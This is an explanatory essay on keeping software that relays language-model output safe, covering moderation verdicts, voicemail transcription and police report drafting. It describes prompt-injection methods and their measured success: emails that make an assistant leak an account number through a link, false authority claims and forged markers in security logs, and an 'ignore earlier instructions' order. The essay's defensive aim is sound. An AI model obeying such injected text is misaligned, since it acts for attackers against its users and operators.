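# Keeping Relay Programs Safe When They Pass On Model-Written Text

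## What a relay program is and how hostile text travels through it

A relay program is ordinary software that passes on what a language model has written. For example, a stranger might fill in the contact form on a museum's website, and a language model might summarize the message in at most 280 characters. The relay program, a script of perhaps twenty lines, puts the words "New enquiry" in front of the summary and posts it to the staff chat channel, using an access token that lets it post under the museum's name. The script contains no artificial intelligence. It always makes the same post from the same summary, and a programmer could confirm in five minutes that it does nothing else.

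That predictability covers only the step from summary to post. The stranger chose the message that shaped the summary, and the script posts the summary whatever it contains, so someone with no account on the museum's chat system has some control over what appears there. Security engineers call anything an outsider could have written or altered *untrusted text*, whether it arrives as a form, an email, a recording or a web page. A summary of untrusted text is also untrusted. The *receiver* is whatever gets the relayed text next, which here is the chat program and then the staff.

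### Prompt injection

The stranger can try to steer the summary by *prompt injection*, which means placing instructions in untrusted text so that the model follows them as if they came from its user or operator. The term dates from 2022. In *A Lifecycle and Application-Stack Survey of Large Language Model Vulnerabilities*, Natanzi and Tang (2026) call the attack indirect when the instructions sit in outside material that an application later feeds to the model. They distinguish prompt injection from jailbreaking, which usually means getting a model to break its safety rules. An injected instruction can succeed without breaking those rules, for example by getting the model to put a false phone number in a summary.

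The attack works because the museum's software puts the stranger's message in the same prompt as its own instruction to summarise the enquiry. *Prompt injection is not SQL injection* (2025), a post by David C for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, contrasts this with a database. A database engine can take a query and a value separately, and it will then never run the value as a command. A language model only predicts the next token, or fragment of text, from all the text before it. Developers can make attacks harder by training a model to favour its operator's instructions or by marking the outside text as data, but neither method creates the separation that a database has.

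It is less clear how often attackers succeed in practice. The Open Worldwide Application Security Project (OWASP), a non-profit foundation, puts prompt injection first in its 2026 ranking of security risks for applications built on language models. But prompt injection would have missed the top ten if the ranking had used recorded incidents alone, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Prompt Injection Remains Biggest LLM Risk, Despite Limited Incidents*. OWASP says this is because teams work hard to fight injection, so few clean cases reach a public database. That may be right, but the count would also be low if the threat were smaller than practitioners think. In either case, it makes sense to follow OWASP's design advice, which is to assume that the model will at some point follow the wrong instructions and to limit what its output can reach.

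### The confused deputy

Programs that misuse their authority on an outsider's behalf are much older than language models. *The Confused Deputy* (Hardy, 1988) tells a "nearly true story" from Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. Tymshare kept its compiler in a directory called SYSX and gave it permission to write files there so that it could record usage statistics. Users could also name a file to receive debugging output. One user gave the name of the company's billing file, which was also in SYSX. The operating system allowed the compiler to open that file because the compiler had permission to write in SYSX, and the debugging output replaced the billing records.

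The user did not need to break in, because the compiler had the authority the user lacked and applied it to a file name the user chose. A *confused deputy* is a program that someone with less authority tricks into misusing its authority in this way. Hardy attributed the fault to the compiler having authority from two sources, the user and its place in SYSX, with no way to keep them apart. He also observed that the code for writing output was correct when its programmers wrote it. It became wrong when Tymshare granted the extra permission, and to discover that, someone would have had to examine every situation in which the compiler wrote a file.

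The museum's script could go wrong in the same way. At first, the worst it can do is make a bad post. Suppose a colleague later connects the channel to a second program that issues ticket refunds whenever a post has a certain form. Strangers may now be able to trigger refunds through the script, even though nobody has changed it.

Hardy's solution was the *capability*, a reference that both identifies a file and authorises the holder to write to it. The compiler would write debugging output using only the reference the user gave it, so the user's request could never rely on the compiler's own permission. David C doubts that language models can be fixed so completely, calling them "inherently confusable" and recommending limits on the surrounding system to reduce the risk. One such limit, from an online exchange between the developers Simon Willison and Baibhav Bista, is that a model's privileges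 should drop to those of the party whose text it is processing. Under that rule, while the museum's model reads a stranger's message, it may do only what the museum would let a stranger do.

### Four failures

Hostile text that gets past the model can do harm in four ways, and a safeguard against one is often useless against another.

A receiver may treat content as a command. OWASP's *LLM05:2025 Improper Output Handling* defines the weakness behind this as insufficient validation, sanitisation and handling of model output before it goes to other components. The examples include a system shell that runs the model's text, a browser that executes a script inside it, and a database that runs it as a query. In one scenario, a chatbot passes its model's reply straight to an extension that also has administrative functions, and the extension shuts down for maintenance. The usual remedy is escaping,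 which means rewriting the text so that a particular receiver treats every character as content. Improper output handling fell from fifth place to last in OWASP's 2026 ranking, but Invicti's *OWASP LLM Top 10 2026* (2026) notes that the category now also covers terminals that act on control codes in the text and display programs that automatically fetch outside resources the text refers to.

A second model may follow instructions in the text. Escaping doesn't help, because the command can be an ordinary English sentence with no special character to neutralise. *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants* (Willison, 2023) warns that when developers feed one model's output into another, the first model can reproduce an injected instruction, or a modified version of it, for the second. *ChannelGuard* (Hossain, Nipu and colleagues, 2026) tests a filter for these handoffs that compares each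 sentence with twenty known attack phrases, then passes, shortens or blocks the text. The filter blocked all thirty attacks hidden in tool results on each of five models, but on four of those models none of the attacks had succeeded without it. It cut the success rate of direct injections from 80% to 3% on one small open model and from 77% to 10% on another. Reworded attacks still succeeded in 57% to 67% of trials, almost exactly as often as without the filter.

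Private data may leak through the text, which security engineers call *exfiltration*. Dongol (2026), in *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection*, gives a minimal case. Alice asks an assistant to summarise an email. The assistant looks up her account number, reads the email and shows her a summary. The task doesn't require the web, but the assistant also has a tool for fetching web pages, and an instruction in the email makes the model request an address on the attacker's site that contains the account number. A program with no such tool can still leak data. Willison points out that a link can carry encoded data in its address, and that an image reference doesn't need a click because displaying the picture sends the request. These leaks can happen only when the model has access to private data, so the museum's model can't leak any if it sees only the stranger's own message.

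Finally, a person may believe a false statement. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (2025) describes an assistant that sends calendar information to the user's boss. Its design prevents text in the calendar from adding new instructions, but that text can still change the body of the email arbitrarily. The museum's staff might read that a lender has approved the early collection of a painting. The stranger may not need prompt injection for this, because an accurate summary of a false message repeats the false claim. Willison describes a message that goes further by persuading the reader to copy encoded private data and paste it into an attacker's website, which gets around any ban on links and images.

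### How much a verdict can carry

One remedy is to pass on less text. If the staff only need to know whether an enquiry is general, a booking or a complaint, the program can require a *fixed verdict*, accepting the model's output only if it exactly matches an item on a short list that the programmer wrote in advance.

Information theory measures the reduction in bits, where one bit is the answer to one yes-or-no question. An output with *k* possible values carries at most log₂(*k*) bits per call, and reaches that maximum only when all the values are equally likely. Three possible verdicts therefore carry at most log₂(3), or about 1.58 bits. Hossain and colleagues prove the same limit for the three possible decisions of their filter. A free summary of 280 characters, each chosen from 95 printable ones, can carry up to 280 × log₂(95), or about 1,840 bits.

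| What the program accepts | Possible outputs | Most it can carry per call |
|---|---|---|
| Yes or no | 2 | 1 bit |
| One of three verdicts | 3 | 1.58 bits |
| A whole number from 0 to 10 | 11 | 3.46 bits |
| Two such numbers | 121 | 6.92 bits |
| 280 printable characters | 95²⁸⁰ | about 1,840 bits |

Some designs build this ordering into their security rules. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) ranks a yes-or-no answer below a choice from a list, and a choice from a list below free text. A policy can then let an important action depend on a yes-or-no answer drawn from an untrusted email, since the sender controls at most one bit, but not on free text from the same email.

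Jacob, Alghamdi and colleagues (2025) make a slightly different argument in *Preventing Prompt Injection with Type-Directed Privilege Separation*. In their design, the model that reads untrusted text may pass only numbers, true-or-false values and choices from a list to the model that acts. They argue that none of these can express an instruction of the attacker's own. For numbers, this depends on how the receiver reads them and does not follow from the capacity bound. A whole number with no upper limit can encode a text of any length, which a receiver could recover by decoding the number. The team's shopping assistant uses scores from 0 to 10, which also keeps the capacity small, and the design limits the length of lists to prevent decoding.

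The bound applies to each call, so the total that can leak grows with the number of calls. A sixteen-digit number holds about 53 bits, so thirty-four three-way verdicts could reveal one to an outsider who saw them all, if the model choosing the verdicts had the number in its input. The value of *k* must also include every outcome the outsider can tell apart. If the program holds malformed outputs for review and the outsider can notice the hold, there are four outcomes instead of three, and the limit rises to 2 bits. Timing can leak more information. In one of Dongol's examples, Alice approves the exact text of each reply, but an attacker still learns whether a private value equals that text, because a match makes the message go out one step early.

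Capacity limits what someone can smuggle through the program, but not the harm it can do. David C describes a recruiter's system that asks a model whether a CV meets the requirements, and a candidate who hides an instruction in the CV to approve it. The system takes only one bit from the model, but that is enough to get the CV approved. A payment system that asks a model to approve or refuse has the same problem, with more money at stake. The museum can stop strangers from composing posts on its channel by limiting the model to a list of verdicts, but a stranger may still be able to choose the verdict.

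### What "safe" can mean

"Safe" can mean that a relay program takes no unauthorised action, that it leaks nothing, or that the message it delivers is true. Programmers can enforce the first two much more easily than the third.

Preventing unauthorised action mostly means deciding what the program may do, and where its text may go, before any untrusted text arrives. Costa and colleagues give the example of a request to summarise three emails and send the summary to a named user. A model without tools writes the summary, and the model that plans the work handles only a placeholder, a name that stands for the text. Only the user's request then determines whether the summary is sent and who receives it. The summary is still untrusted when it reaches the recipient.

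A guarantee against leaks needs a definition of a leak. The strictest definition, *noninterference*, requires that nothing an outsider sees depends on private data. Dongol objects that this rules out useful programs, such as an assistant that answers meeting requests with its user's free hours. Dongol instead compares the assistant with a reference version that has the same plan and checks but a model that never obeys untrusted text, and counts as a leak only what the real assistant reveals beyond what the reference version would. An injected demand that obtains the calendar therefore causes no leak, because a genuine meeting request would have obtained it too, but one that obtains a password reset code does.

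Using that definition, Dongol gives a machine-checked proof that an assistant meets the standard if, by the time it first reads untrusted text, it has permanently given up every tool that an injection could call. The theorem assumes that the assistant fixed its plan beforehand, that each injection triggers a single call, and that the attacker sees the content and order of messages but not their timing. Giving up tools can severely limit the assistant. For example, it cannot answer an email it has just read if it has given up its sending tool. A program that blocks every call also meets the standard, so a developer has to test separately whether the program still does its job.

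No comparable theorem can guarantee that the text is true. Nobody can tell from the summary alone whether the lender approved the collection of the painting. Jacob and colleagues exclude misleading or bogus input from the threats they defend against. Their shopping assistant still offers partial protection, because it turns each product review into scores and takes the median. A single dishonest reviewer among many can shift the result only a little, but a seller who writes most of the reviews can shift it as far as the scale allows. The museum's script has only one message to go on, and about the best it can do is mark the post as an unverified claim from outside, so that someone rings the lender before the painting leaves.

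## Moderation pipelines: reducing model output to a fixed verdict

Content moderation, which checks users' posts against a site's rules, is well suited to a fixed verdict. The program that acts on a post only needs to know which rule, if any, the post breaks, so the model can read a long abusive post and pass on a single word. But the post's author writes most of what the model reads, and often has the most to gain from a wrong verdict.

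### From comment to action

GitHub (2025), which hosts software projects, announced an AI moderator that maintainers can add to their projects. Suppose a stranger replies to a bug report with an advertisement for cheap watches. According to GitHub's *AI Moderator* (2025), the new comment starts an ordinary script, which uses three prompts to have a model check the comment for spam, suspicious links and AI-generated text. If the model detects spam, the script collapses the comment. If the offending post is a new issue (a bug report or a request), the script labels it instead. The maintainer sets the label names in advance, and the defaults are "spam" and "ai-generated".

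The script's access token would also let it post comments and close issues. The watch seller can't use the model to trigger those actions as long as the script uses the answers only to decide whether to label or collapse. Three yes-or-no answers carry at most three bits. GitHub's *Agent of the Day* (2026) describes a more elaborate moderator, an AI agent that investigates each post, in one case over sixteen turns, before deciding whether to label it, hide it, escalate it or leave it alone. The extra reasoning may improve the verdict, but the agent still chooses from a short list of outcomes.

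The prompt usually contains more than the comment. *Scaling Reinforcement Learning for Content Moderation with Large Language Models* (Liu, Lu and colleagues, 2025) describes a program at Meta that joins an instruction, the relevant policy and the content. Its example prompt also includes the author's username, biography and recent posts, which are untrusted text too. Sam, in *Discourse AI*, gives a similar list for the spam scanner in Discourse, a program for running online forums. The scanner sends the model only the first 5,000 characters of the post, so an advertisement placed after that point never reaches the model.

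When Discourse's scanner checks a reply, it also sends the model up to 500 characters of the post being answered. An instruction placed in that post by another user could lead the model to class a newcomer's reply as spam, and the scanner would then hide the reply and silence the newcomer until a moderator resolved the flag. Limiting the model to a fixed verdict doesn't prevent this, because "spam" is one of the permitted answers.

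### Reading the verdict

The model's answer arrives as text, and the program has to turn it into an action. Suppose a programmer asks for one word, "safe" or "unsafe", and then searches the reply:

```python
if "safe" in reply:
    publish(comment)
else:
    hide(comment)
```

The word "unsafe" contains "safe", so this program publishes every comment that the model rejects. Better-chosen words would fix that fault but leave another. Models often explain themselves, and an explanation may quote the comment, so a commenter can supply the word that the program is looking for. An exact match avoids both problems:

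```python
ACTIONS = {"safe": publish, "unsafe": hide}

action = ACTIONS.get(reply, hold_for_review)
action(comment)
```

The first line lists the only two replies the program accepts. If the reply is anything else, or is empty or missing, the program sends the comment to a person. The program therefore *fails closed*, meaning it rejects or holds an item when the model's output is missing, malformed or unexpected.

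| Model's reply | Searching for "safe" | Exact match |
|---|---|---|
| safe | publish | publish |
| unsafe | publish | hide |
| The author calls the download "safe", but it is malware. | publish | hold for review |
| Safe. | hide | hold for review |
| (empty) | hide | hold for review |

The fourth reply is a nuisance because it is plainly an approval. The programmer can make the comparison ignore capitalization, spaces and full stops, and the program will still accept only two words.

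Deployed software does use text searches. In Discourse's AI triage feature, an administrator names a piece of text, and the forum acts if it appears anywhere in the model's reply. Discourse's *Setting up spam detection in your community* warns administrators to avoid similar wording for the two results and suggests "spam" and "ham". This advice is good but easy to miss. In the discussion below Sam's guide, a user testing the newer scanner told the model to answer "NOT SPAM" for acceptable posts, which a search for "SPAM" would match. Even with "spam" and "ham", a reply that quotes the word "spam" from an innocent post will trigger the penalty.

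Discourse's triage also fails open. The administrator specifies only the reply that marks a post as bad, so any other reply leaves the post up, and the sample prompt includes an instruction to answer "ham" when unsure. Failing open is defensible for a forum, though it would be a poor choice for a program that releases payments. Forum members can report spam that gets through, whereas a false alarm can delete someone's post and silence its author.

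A list of verdicts in the prompt does not limit the output unless the code enforces it. In a guide for maintainers, GitHub gives a sample script that asks a model to answer "spam", "ai-generated", "needs-review" or "ok". The code checks only for "ok" and turns any other reply into a label, and GitHub creates the label if it doesn't exist. If the model writes "ok" with a full stop, the project gets a new label reading "ok." A stranger who can steer the reply could put a short message of their own on the project's page. (The script also pastes the reply into its own source code, a worse fault that belongs with GitHub automation.)

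The same script is supposed to handle pull requests (proposed changes to a project's code), but it takes the item number from a field that exists only for issues. The labelling step therefore stops with an error if the model reports a pull request as spam, and the spam stays unlabelled. This failure can happen without an attacker, and a test with one spam pull request would have exposed it.

Many programs ask for JSON, a standard format for structured data, instead of a single word. In the format that Liu and colleagues use, the model writes out its reasoning and then a JSON object that answers each policy question with true or false. Their sample reply puts these values in quotation marks, which makes them pieces of text. In Python, any non-empty text counts as true, so this line would remove a comment that the model had cleared with the answer "false":

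```python
if verdict["violation"]:
    remove(comment)
```

A stricter program removes the comment only if the value is the JSON boolean true, publishes it only if the value is the JSON boolean false, and holds it in every other case. The program should also discard the model's reasoning and require the rest of the reply to be one valid JSON object. A program that instead takes the first object in the reply will read the commenter's verdict if the commenter wrote one in JSON and the model quoted it while reasoning.

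Sample code from Anthropic passes the whole reply to a JSON parser, which raises an error if the reply is malformed. OpenAI's sample raises an error when the moderation check itself fails. If the site publishes a comment only after receiving a verdict, either error keeps the comment out of sight. GitHub's moderator starts after the comment is public, so a crash leaves the advertisement for watches on the page. To fail closed there, the program would have to hide the comment on any error until someone had looked at it.

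### Thresholds and token probabilities

A language model assigns a probability to every possible next token, and a program can use those probabilities to measure how confident a verdict is. Liu and colleagues write the rule as

ŷ = 1 if P(y = 1 | q) ≥ τ, and otherwise ŷ = 0,

where *q* is the whole prompt, *y* = 1 means that the content breaks the policy, and τ is a threshold between 0 and 1. They choose τ by testing it on labelled examples. A site that dreads false accusations would set it high, and one that dreads missed abuse would set it low.

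The threshold works badly if the model reasons before answering. By the time it reaches the verdict, its own reasoning has usually stated the conclusion, so the probability of "true" is close to either 0 or 1 even in a doubtful case. Liu and colleagues deal with this by sampling several lines of reasoning and averaging the results:

P(y = 1 | q) ≈ (1/N) × Σ P(y = 1 | rᵢ, q),

where *r*ᵢ is the *i*-th of *N* samples. Suppose seven samples out of ten end with a probability of 0.99 and three with 0.01. The average is 0.696, which a site with a threshold of 0.9 would not treat as a violation. A single sample would have given 0.99 about seven times in ten, and the site would have removed the comment. The better estimate costs ten model calls instead of one.

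A program can also avoid parsing a reply by reading the model's probabilities instead. *Lessons from Defending Gemini Against Indirect Prompt Injections* (Shi, Lin and colleagues, 2025) describes a classifier at Google that asks a model whether some material contains a prompt injection. The program compares the probabilities of "yes" and "no" and reports an injection if "yes" is more likely. Because it doesn't search a reply, a quotation or a stray full stop can't cause an error. It still needs a rule for failing closed. If "yes" has a probability of 0.02 and "no" has 0.01, the program reports an injection although the model would almost certainly have written something else. A careful program would hold the item unless the two probabilities added up to at least, say, 0.9.

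This method made the verdict easy to read, but the verdict was often wrong. On Gemini 1.5 Pro, the classifier caught between 95.7% and 97.6% of attacks but also flagged 31.1% of emails that contained no injection. On the smaller Gemini 1.5 Flash, it caught 63.6% to 89% of attacks and flagged 82.1% of clean emails. Shi and colleagues attribute the false alarms to using a classifier trained to spot unsafe content and using ordinary spam as the clean emails. They suggest tuning a threshold to reach a chosen false alarm rate. In another test, they asked Gemini itself for a written yes or no, and false alarms fell to 2% on Pro and to zero on Flash. But the detection rate depended heavily on the wording of the question, ranging from 22.8% to 81.6% across three descriptions of prompt injection.

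A classifier that reads hostile text can also be manipulated by it, as Shi and colleagues acknowledge. Their most effective defence was a classifier that received only the user's request and the assistant's proposed action, without the email, and judged whether the action plausibly followed from the request. Moderators can't use this defence because they have to judge the untrusted text itself.

### Valid verdicts that are wrong

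In *Poisoning the Watchtower*, Pandey and Bhujang (2026) measured how often an attacker can choose the verdict when a language model sorts security logs, which are a company's records of requests to its servers. Analysts increasingly use language models for this task, and attackers write much of the logs' content, including the web addresses they request and the usernames they try. An intruder can therefore put a message to the model in the same request as the attack.

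The experiment tested GPT-4o-mini, a small OpenAI model from 2024, on artificial logs. In each condition, the model saw 120 malicious logs containing an injection and 80 harmless logs without one. It had to label each log, summarise it or recommend a response. The injections took four forms: a plain order to ignore earlier instructions; a false claim to speak for the security team; forged markers that imitated the end of the log and an official conclusion; and an order disguised as encoded data.

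Pandey and Bhujang tested each form under four defence modes. One had no defence. Another wrapped each field in tags and warned the model that the contents were data. A third kept those tags and added a filter that removed suspicious phrases from the logs. The fourth also kept the tags, but let the system return only a label from a short list or one of a few prewritten sentences.

The plain order and the encoded order never produced a false "benign" label. The table shows how often the false claim of authority and the forged markers did, as a percentage of the malicious logs.

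| Task | Attack | No defence | Tags | Tags and filter | Tags and fixed outputs |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Label | False authority | 68 | 15 | 22 | 33 |
| Label | Forged markers | 17 | 17 | 22 | 16 |
| Summary | False authority | 49 | 44 | 35 | 24 |
| Summary | Forged markers | 96 | 75 | 27 | 38 |
| Recommendation | False authority | 34 | 11 | 21 | 20 |
| Recommendation | Forged markers | 39 | 37 | 8 | 10 |

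Fixed outputs prevented any of the attacker's wording from reaching the analyst, regardless of how the model behaved. But the false claim of authority still led the model to label about 40 of the 120 malicious logs benign, and the forged markers spoiled 38% of summaries.

Fixed outputs should be compared with tags alone, since both modes used tags. Fixed outputs roughly halved the success rates for summaries. For labels, they seem to have raised the success rate of the false claim of authority from 15% to 33%, well outside the margin of error of seven to nine points. Pandey and Bhujang suggest that a model forced into a binary choice defers more readily to the supposed authority. This explanation is doubtful because the list they describe also included "suspicious", so the choice was not binary. The program applied the restriction after the model had answered, so the rise could also have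 come from how the program converted hedged answers into labels.

Fixed outputs do make errors easier to find. When the model wrote free-form summaries with no defence, the forged markers succeeded 96% of the time, but the model never explicitly labelled a log "benign". It left out the attack or played it down, so a program searching the summaries for "benign" would have found nothing wrong. With fixed outputs, an auditor can at least pull every log marked benign and check a sample.

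These rates come from one old model and may be quite different for a current one. The plain order never succeeded on undefended labels, although a simulated analyst that Pandey and Bhujang built from earlier research predicted that it would succeed 92% of the time. A developer who tried only that well-known attack would have wrongly concluded that the system was safe.

They advise against letting the model recommend inaction unless a program can check the evidence for it. A moderation program can apply the same idea by letting the model flag a comment but never remove a flag. If an ordinary rule finds a link to a known malware site, the comment stays hidden whatever the model outputs. An injected claim of authority can then get a comment approved only if no rule flagged that comment. The drawback is that people have to clear the comments that rules flag by mistake.

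### Screening citizens' opinions

A verdict can also decide what another model gets to read. In the doctoral thesis *Large Language Models and Augmented Democracy*, Gudiño-Rosero (2026) tested this in a system that turns several citizens' opinions on a public question into a consensus statement. Each question had three to six opinions, taken from a 2023 experiment in the United Kingdom. Gudiño-Rosero replaced one opinion in each group with an injection and counted how often the statement changed its position between agreement, disagreement and ambiguity. With no defence, statements from a small open Meta model changed position in 57.9% of cases.

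Gudiño-Rosero then added a guard, a second model that read each opinion separately and returned 1 for an injection and 0 for a genuine opinion. The program replaced any opinion marked 1 with the words "Opinion Deleted". The guard flagged 99.31% of the injections and none of the genuine opinions, but the consensus statement still changed position in 47.7% of cases.

Missed injections can't explain much of that, since the guard let through fewer than one in a hundred. The remaining problem lay mostly in the next step. Small models are bad at counting opinions and applying a majority rule, according to Gudiño-Rosero, and deleting the injection did not make this one better at it. Reducing each opinion to a position and a short list of reasons brought the rate down to 41.6%. Training the model to write out a tally before the statement brought it down to 20.2%, while giving an untrained model a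 calculator for the tally instead brought it down to 29.6%. Even when nobody was attacking, the full set of defences changed the position of about 15% of statements.

The guard may do worse in use than it did in testing. Gudiño-Rosero wrote the injections from forty templates, none designed to fool this guard, and warns that attackers will study any detector whose workings are public. False alarms are also more serious here than on a forum, because each one removes a citizen from the count. The guard's instructions forbade participants to mention AI at all, but one question in the data was about the use of algorithms in hiring, and an honest answer could easily break that rule.

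The guard also returned a short rationale with its verdict, but the program needs only the 1 or 0. The rationale comes from a model that has just read untrusted text, so passing it to the model that writes the consensus would give an injection another route to that model.

### Explaining a removal

People whose comments are removed usually want to know why, and the model can easily generate an explanation. Anthropic's sample format has a true-or-false field for the violation, a list of categories and an optional explanation. If a site publishes that explanation, it is again posting free text that a stranger has influenced, and doing so under its own name. A commenter could try to get a link, an insult or an accusation against another user into the official notice.

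A moderation model's explanation may not be the real reason for its verdict. When Liu and colleagues trained moderation models by rewarding correct verdicts, the reasoning shrank from about 250 words to fewer than 50. They found that the models increasingly wrote justifications to fit the expected answer instead of reasoning from the content. A fluent explanation like this could lead an author to rewrite the wrong sentence.

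Alternatively, the site's staff can write one notice for each rule. The model returns a category, and the program checks it against the list and selects the matching notice. In Discourse, an administrator can write a fixed reply or have a second model compose each reply. OpenAI's developer forum has used a fixed reply for posts from people who thought they were talking to ChatGPT, which made up about 5% of posts by new users. The model returned "ok" or "bad", and for a bad post the software hid the topic from the listings and posted a prepared explanation. A volunteer moderator there reported that the system was useful but made mistakes, and that many people who received the reply by mistake didn't know how to object.

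Stock notices are less helpful than a good explanation. Someone who wrote six paragraphs learns that the comment was abusive but not which sentence caused the problem. The site can recover some of that detail by writing more specific rules, each with its own notice. It can also ask the model for the start and end positions of the offending passage, check that both fall inside the comment, and have the code quote the passage back to the author. For a 500-character comment, the two positions carry about 17 bits, and the author receives only their own text. The site should send this notice privately, because a public one would republish the abuse.

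Neither improvement helps when the verdict is wrong. A stock notice accusing an innocent person of spamming is as false as one written by a model, and it looks more official, so every notice should explain how to appeal.

### Rewriting a message instead of blocking it

Roblox, an online gaming platform popular with children, has gone further and lets a model change what users write to each other. It used to replace forbidden chat messages with a row of hash marks, a minimal stock notice. The company's *Rethinking Chat for Fun, Gameplay, and Civility* (2026) calls those marks a dead end for conversation. It gives the example of a player who swears while warning a friend about a monster, so the friend sees only "###########".

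Since March 2026, Roblox has used a model to rewrite chat messages that contain profanity. "Hurry tf up!" becomes "Hurry up!", and everyone in the chat sees a notice that the text has changed. The original message still counts as a violation, and someone who keeps swearing faces the same penalties as before. The feature works only in in-game chats, which are open to age-checked users in similar age groups and their approved contacts. Roblox admits that the feature won't always rephrase messages perfectly.

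Prompt injection is less dangerous here than in a removal notice. The rewritten message appears under the sender's name, to people the sender could already message, so a player who tricks the model into writing a permitted sentence could have typed it themselves. The trick would help the player only if the model produced something the filter would have blocked, such as a phone number. Running the filter again on the rewritten text guards against this, within the limits of what the filter can detect.

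The greater risk is to the honest sender, because a rewrite can change a joke into an insult or a refusal into an agreement, and the other players will read it as the sender's own words. They can learn from the notice that something has changed, but not what the sender meant.

A program can avoid this in simple cases by making the edit itself. According to GamesBeat's *Roblox rolls out real-time rephrasing feature for profanity*, the feature either removes the offending words or swaps them for milder ones. For removal, the model can point to the forbidden words without writing any text, and the code can delete them, turning "Hurry tf up!" into "Hurry up!". To stop the model from deleting a word such as "not", the code can accept only deletions of words on a list of profanities, although it will then miss new slang and unusual spellings. Deletion also fails on the warning about the monster,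 because the sentence ends with a crude word for the friend's backside and is incomplete without it. The program would therefore need a list of approved substitutes too. Roblox offers rephrasing in every language that its automatic translation covers, and keeping such lists current in all of them would take a lot of work.

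## Transcription pipelines: when all the text has to pass

Unlike a moderation program, which can discard a comment's words once it has a verdict on them, a transcription program has to deliver the words. Suppose the museum also has a voicemail line and wants each message in writing. The label "complaint" is little use to someone who needs to know which painting the caller meant and what number to call back. If the caller swears, lies or reads out an instruction aimed at a language model, an accurate transcript has to include those words.

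So a fixed verdict can't protect this program. A one-minute message has perhaps 150 words, or 900 characters, which could carry up to about 5,900 bits, compared with 1.58 for a three-way verdict. The museum can still limit what the text triggers when it arrives and make sure someone can check the text against the recording.

### From recording to record

The message goes through five steps. The phone system saves a recording. A speech recognition model turns the recording into a raw transcript. A language model then adds punctuation, removes the "ums" and may summarise the message. A script puts the result into a template with the caller's number and the time. The script then emails the page to the front desk or files it as a record.

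At the third step, a sentence spoken over the phone can work as a prompt injection against the clean-up model. It can do the same to an AI assistant if staff later ask one to go through their email. Accurate copying doesn't prevent this. In the case of Grok and Bankrbot, a payment program treated a decoded Morse-code message as a command.

If the clean-up model has no tools, an injection can only spoil the transcript. For light editing, a few lines of code can prevent most of that too:

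```python
import re

FILLERS = {"um", "uh", "er"}

def spoken_words(text):
    words = re.findall(r"[\w']+", text.lower())
    return [word for word in words if word not in FILLERS]

if spoken_words(cleaned) != spoken_words(transcript):
    cleaned = transcript
```

The model may add punctuation, capitals and paragraph breaks, and it may drop the three filler words. If it changes anything else, the program uses the raw transcript. This check prevents an injected instruction from adding or removing a phone number, though an added question mark can still turn a statement into a question. The check doesn't work for summaries, because a good summary uses different words from the original.

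### A police report about a frog

Draft One, a product of the police technology company Axon, turns the audio from an officer's body camera into a draft police report. It uses a variant of ChatGPT and works only from the dialogue, not the video.

In December 2025 the police department in Heber City, Utah, was testing Draft One and a rival product, Code Four. According to FOX 13 News' *Ribbit ribbit! Artificial Intelligence programs used by Heber City police*, Draft One produced a report in which an officer turned into a frog. Sergeant Rick Keel explained that the Disney film *The Princess and the Frog* had been playing in the background, and Axios' *How AI turned a Utah police officer into a frog* (2026) gives the same explanation. A conflicting account in the AI Incident Database quotes someone named Sever, who remembers a similar sentence but blames a Harry Potter film. That account says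 only that Heber City was testing "similar software". In both versions, the software put dialogue from a television into a report as if it described what had happened.

The error came from treating a film character's lines as events at the scene. The speech recognition may have worked perfectly, since the film's dialogue was audible, but without the video, the software had no way to detect the television in the room. An officer will notice a frog in a draft report. If the television had been showing a crime drama, though, the draft might have included a threat or a gun, and an officer reading it at the end of a shift could easily have left that in. Nobody was attacking the system in this case, but a bystander could also say something near the camera on purpose to get it into the draft.

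Some of Draft One's safeguards are ordinary software. The program puts bracketed placeholders in the draft where the officer should add observations, and it asks the officer to sign a statement that they have reviewed and corrected the report. The Electronic Frontier Foundation (EFF), a digital rights group that opposes AI-written police reports, examined these features in July 2025 using public records and Axon's manuals. It found that officers can delete the brackets instead of filling them in. A stricter program would withhold the text until the officer had filled in every blank, but it still wouldn't draw attention to a false sentence between the blanks. An officer can also sign the statement without reading the draft. Axon told one Colorado department that, at least three times, a bug had let officers bypass the safeguards against submitting unread drafts.

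EFF's main complaint was about record-keeping. Draft One doesn't save its original draft or any later version. The officer copies the text into the police report, and the draft disappears when the window closes. The log records that an officer requested a draft, signed the statement or changed the settings, but not what the draft contained. The police in Lafayette, Indiana, told EFF that they couldn't list the reports written with Draft One. The sheriff's office in Palm Beach County, Florida, requires a sentence at the bottom of each such report disclosing the use of AI. By searching for that sentence, it found more than 3,000 reports from a four-month period.

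Axon's product manager for generative AI told a roundtable that the company discards the drafts "by design", because it did not want to create "more disclosure headaches" for its customers and their attorneys. Another Axon executive argued that an officer using a word processor wouldn't have to keep every draft either. Axon also promotes its audit log as the main transparency measure, according to EFF.

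The word-processor comparison is weak because an officer who types a report is responsible for every sentence, while a false sentence in a report that began in Draft One may have come from the software or the officer. Without the draft, the only evidence of which one introduced it is the officer's memory. The body-camera recording can show that the sentence is false but not where it came from. Storing drafts is easy, since each takes up a few kilobytes. When EFF wrote, California legislators were considering SB 524, a bill that would require police to keep the first draft for as long as the final report.

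### Words nobody said

The film's dialogue was in the recording, but speech recognisers also write fluent sentences that nobody spoke, which researchers call *hallucinations*. Most of the research concerns Whisper, a recogniser that OpenAI released in 2022. It is still widely used. Zolkepli (2026) counts about 4.6 million downloads a month for one version in *How to Reduce Whisper Hallucination*.

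Koenecke, Choi and colleagues (2024) made the problem widely known with *Careless Whisper*. In April and May 2023, they ran 13,140 short clips through Whisper, taken from interviews with a control group and with people who had aphasia, a language disorder that often follows a stroke. About 1.4% of the transcripts contained invented text, and 38% of those inventions were harmful. Some added violence, some made up names, relationships or illnesses, and some included instructions to visit a website. When one speaker described calling the fire department to rescue a father and a cat, Whisper added a "blood-soaked stroller" to the transcript.

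Invented text appeared in the transcripts of 1.7% of clips from speakers with aphasia and 1.2% of clips from the control group. Pauses may explain the difference, because on average 41% of a recording from a speaker with aphasia contained no voice, compared with 15% in the control group. By December 2023, after OpenAI had updated Whisper, only 12 of the 187 clips that had produced invented text still did.

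Each of those clips contained about a sentence of speech, and the rate is far higher when there is none. Barański, Jasiński and colleagues (2025), in *Investigation of Whisper ASR Hallucinations Induced by Non-Speech Audio*, gave Whisper 301,317 recordings of noises, animals, machines and silence, and it wrote words for 40.3% of them. A voicemail from someone who forgets to hang up could contain several minutes of noise or silence.

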